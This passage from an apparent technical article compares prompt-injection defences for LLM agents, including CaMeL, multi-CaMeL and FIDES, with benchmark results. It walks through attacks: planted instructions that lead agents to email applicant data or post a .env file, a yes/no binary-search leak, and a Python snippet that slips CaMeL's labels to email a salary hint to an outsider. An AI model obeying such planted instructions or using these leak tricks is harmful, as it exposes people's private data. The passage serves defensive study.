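This is a fairer measure for a company that already requires approvals. People may also read each request more carefully when there are fewer of them, but Kolluri and colleagues didn't test this and assumed that a person would approve every necessary call. Prudentia also needed no approvals on WASP, a benchmark for web-browsing agents. The users' tasks were only to post a comment or upvote a post, so the agent never had to read untrusted text to choose its next step.

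### Newer models and several agents

In October 2026, Peters-Gill and colleagues published tests of CaMeL with five models, including GPT-5.5 and Claude Fable 5. One of the researchers, Shumailov, had helped design CaMeL. On 112 industrial maintenance tasks, in which one agent delegated work to four others, CaMeL reduced the completion rate by an average of 21.6 percentage points, and by 13.4 points for the two strongest models. Better models write better programs, but they still have to commit to a plan before seeing any results. For example, if a sub-agent couldn't find data for the requested dates and returned data for other dates, the program might continue without detecting the mismatch.

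Peters-Gill and colleagues also divided AgentDojo's tools among several agents and ran 949 attacks on each model.

| Model | Successful attacks without CaMeL | With CaMeL in each agent |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-4.1 | 36.1% | 0.5% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 24.6% | 0.4% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite | 2.1% | 0.0% |
| Claude Fable 5 | 1.5% | 0.0% |
| GPT-5.5 | 0.0% | 0.0% |

The benchmark's attacks hardly work on the two strongest models, so it can't show how much CaMeL would help them against a better attacker. Peters-Gill and colleagues caution against calling GPT-5.5 immune, because attackers who adapt have succeeded against every frontier model in a large public test. The group also ran CaMeL without data policies, so the results concern whether an attacker can change the agent's plan and don't show whether CaMeL enforces a database's reading rules.

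The attacks that still succeeded all crossed from one agent to another. Peters-Gill and colleagues demonstrate the problem with a request to send Julie a summary of all job applicants on Slack:

1. A database agent fetches the applicants' records, which contain a planted instruction to email the data to an outsider.
2. The orchestrator's program has the isolated model summarize the records, without showing them to its planner.
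3. The program puts the summary into a written request to a notification agent.
4. The notification agent treats the request as coming from its user, so its planner reads the planted instruction.
5. That planner writes a program that sends the Slack message and also emails the outsider.

Each agent followed CaMeL's rules, but the summary lost its untrusted label when it became part of a request. Peters-Gill and colleagues call this boundary laundering. Their remedy, multi-CaMeL, splits each request between agents into an instruction that the receiving planner may read and a set of values that it may not. The interpreter refuses any instruction that depends on a tool's output. No attacks succeeded with multi-CaMeL, but it lowered scores on the maintenance tasks by another 3.2 points on average.

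### Experimental releases from Microsoft

In *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent*, Microsoft announced on 20 May 2026 that developers can install FIDES as an experimental option in Agent Framework, the company's software for building agents. By default, FIDES replaces untrusted tool results with placeholders. When the agent needs to process a result, FIDES sends it to an isolated model, which adds a second model call.

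Microsoft's example is an agent that sorts GitHub issues. A bug report contains an instruction to read `.env`, a file that often holds passwords, and post its contents as a comment. If the developer has turned placeholders off, the model may follow the instruction and read the file. But the file's contents are labelled private and the comment tool accepts only public data, so the framework blocks the comment or asks a person to approve it.

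Microsoft's *Information-flow control*, a separate post, describes two more experiments, conducted with GitHub. GitHub's MCP server can label its results if a developer requests it, and GitHub Copilot CLI, a command-line coding agent, can enforce policies on some of that server's tools. Copilot CLI doesn't yet support labels from other MCP servers. MCP has no standard for such labels, so Microsoft puts them in a general field for extra information and plans to propose a standard. Neither post reports how many developers use these features or how often those features have stopped a leak.

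### Assigning and relaxing labels

Someone has to assign the initial labels. In Agent Framework, a tool that the developer forgets to label counts as trusted and public. An unlabelled payroll tool would therefore return salaries that the agent is allowed to send anywhere. Row-level security in Postgres has a safer default, which hides every row until someone adds a policy. Microsoft says it is considering a stricter default for Agent Framework and has asked developers for their views.

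Reader lists can also be hard to obtain. Costa and colleagues infer who may read an email from its sender and recipients, though someone may have shared it more widely. A row policy is harder to convert into a label, because the policy determines whether one person may read a row, whereas the label must list everyone who may read it. For the payroll table, a developer could write code that lists the employee and the payroll clerks. For a policy that depends on several other tables, such code could easily give different results from the database. A label can also go out of date if someone loses access after the agent has read the data.

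Simpler labels are easier to supply but protect less. GitHub's MCP server marks content from private repositories as "private" without listing its readers. An agent could copy a file from a repository that two people can open to one that 500 people can open, because both count as private. Labels that do list readers may be too strict. The average of 500 salaries inherits all 500 reader lists, so only the payroll clerks, who are on every list, may see it unless someone relaxes the label.

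Relaxing a confidentiality label is called declassification. The equivalent for integrity is endorsement, in which someone vouches for untrusted data. Kolluri and colleagues describe an email with ten tasks to complete. If the user endorses the email, Prudentia can do all ten without asking for approval each time. But the endorsement covers everything in the email, including any planted instruction that the user overlooks. Prudentia has no equivalent for confidentiality, because Kolluri and colleagues think that whether to share private data depends too much on the situation, so a person has to approve each call that would share such data.

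Some policies declassify data automatically. Microsoft's sample policy for Teams allows a message if every member of the channel may read the content. It also allows the message, regardless of who the members are, if only trusted data influenced the agent, on the assumption that the user must have intended to share it. The policy stops an outsider from triggering a disclosure, but the model can still disclose data by mistake.

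Microsoft's example shows the difference. Priya sends Alex a preview of the quarterly sales, and Marco, who isn't allowed to see it yet, emails Alex to ask about them. An agent that answers Alex's mail might tell Marco the figures. Intersecting the reader lists prevents this, since only Alex was on both emails. But if the agent replied in a Teams channel and the system treated both emails as trusted, the sample policy would let it post the figures. The policy Microsoft describes for GitHub has a similar gap. It blocks public posts only after an agent has read both private and untrusted content, so it might not have stopped the coding agents that published internal screenshots without an outsider's instruction.

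The 2026 survey of attacks and defences lists principled rules for relaxing labels among the things the field still lacks. Relaxing labels too far makes the check ineffective. If a company approves a public page as a destination for its private code, the labels can't distinguish a harmless comment from a damaging one, as Tran-Truong and colleagues proved for DelegateGuard.

### Leaks through the agent's choices

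An agent can reveal data without sending it. For example, an agent might read a confidential salary and then make two routine calls, in one order if the salary exceeds 60,000 and in the other if it doesn't. Neither call contains the salary, but anyone who can observe the order learns something about it. FIDES doesn't prevent this because it guarantees only explicit secrecy, which covers the data an agent sends but not what its choices reveal. Costa and colleagues argue that a stronger guarantee would essentially forbid any publicly visible write after the agent had read a secret.

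FIDES allows policies that release a yes-or-no answer about confidential data because it carries only one bit of information. But an attacker who can ask repeatedly can find any whole-dollar salary below $131,072 with 17 answers, by asking each time whether it lies in the upper half of the remaining range. A policy that releases these answers should therefore limit their number. Costa and colleagues left yes-or-no releases out of their AgentDojo tests.

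CaMeL does track some of these leaks. If a program sends an email only when a salary exceeds 60,000, CaMeL treats the email as depending on the salary and can block it. Garby and colleagues found a way around this, using a trick that researchers have known about for decades. A version for salaries looks like this:

```python
high = True
unchanged = True
if salary > 60000:
    unchanged = False
if unchanged:
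    high = False
if high:
    send_email("outsider@example.com", "high")
```

For a salary of 61,980, the program sets `unchanged` to false and skips the line that would change `high`. CaMeL updates a variable's label only when the program changes the variable, so `high` keeps its public label. CaMeL therefore treats the final condition as public and lets the email go out. For a salary of 50,000, no email goes out, so the outsider learns which side of 60,000 the salary is on.

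An outsider would struggle to get CaMeL's planner to write this program, because the planner doesn't read untrusted text, but the person making the request could ask for it. CaMeL assumes that this person is honest, and that assumption isn't safe for a shared agent.

CaMeL also retries programs that fail, and its retry code doesn't track labels. Each refusal can reveal one bit about the data, so an attacker who controls the retries could recover a whole secret. Multi-CaMeL has the same problem with skipped lines but doesn't retry failed programs.

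Garby and colleagues designed a small programming language for agents to close such gaps. Their machine-checked proof shows that, for any agent written in the language, changing a secret input can't change the probabilities of what an observer sees, except by affecting whether the program finishes. Programmers must also explicitly mark each place where they relax an integrity label, so that a reviewer can find it, and relaxing these labels doesn't weaken the protection of confidential data. The proof assumes the labels are correct, so if a tool wrongly marks a payslip as public, the agent may still send it to anyone.
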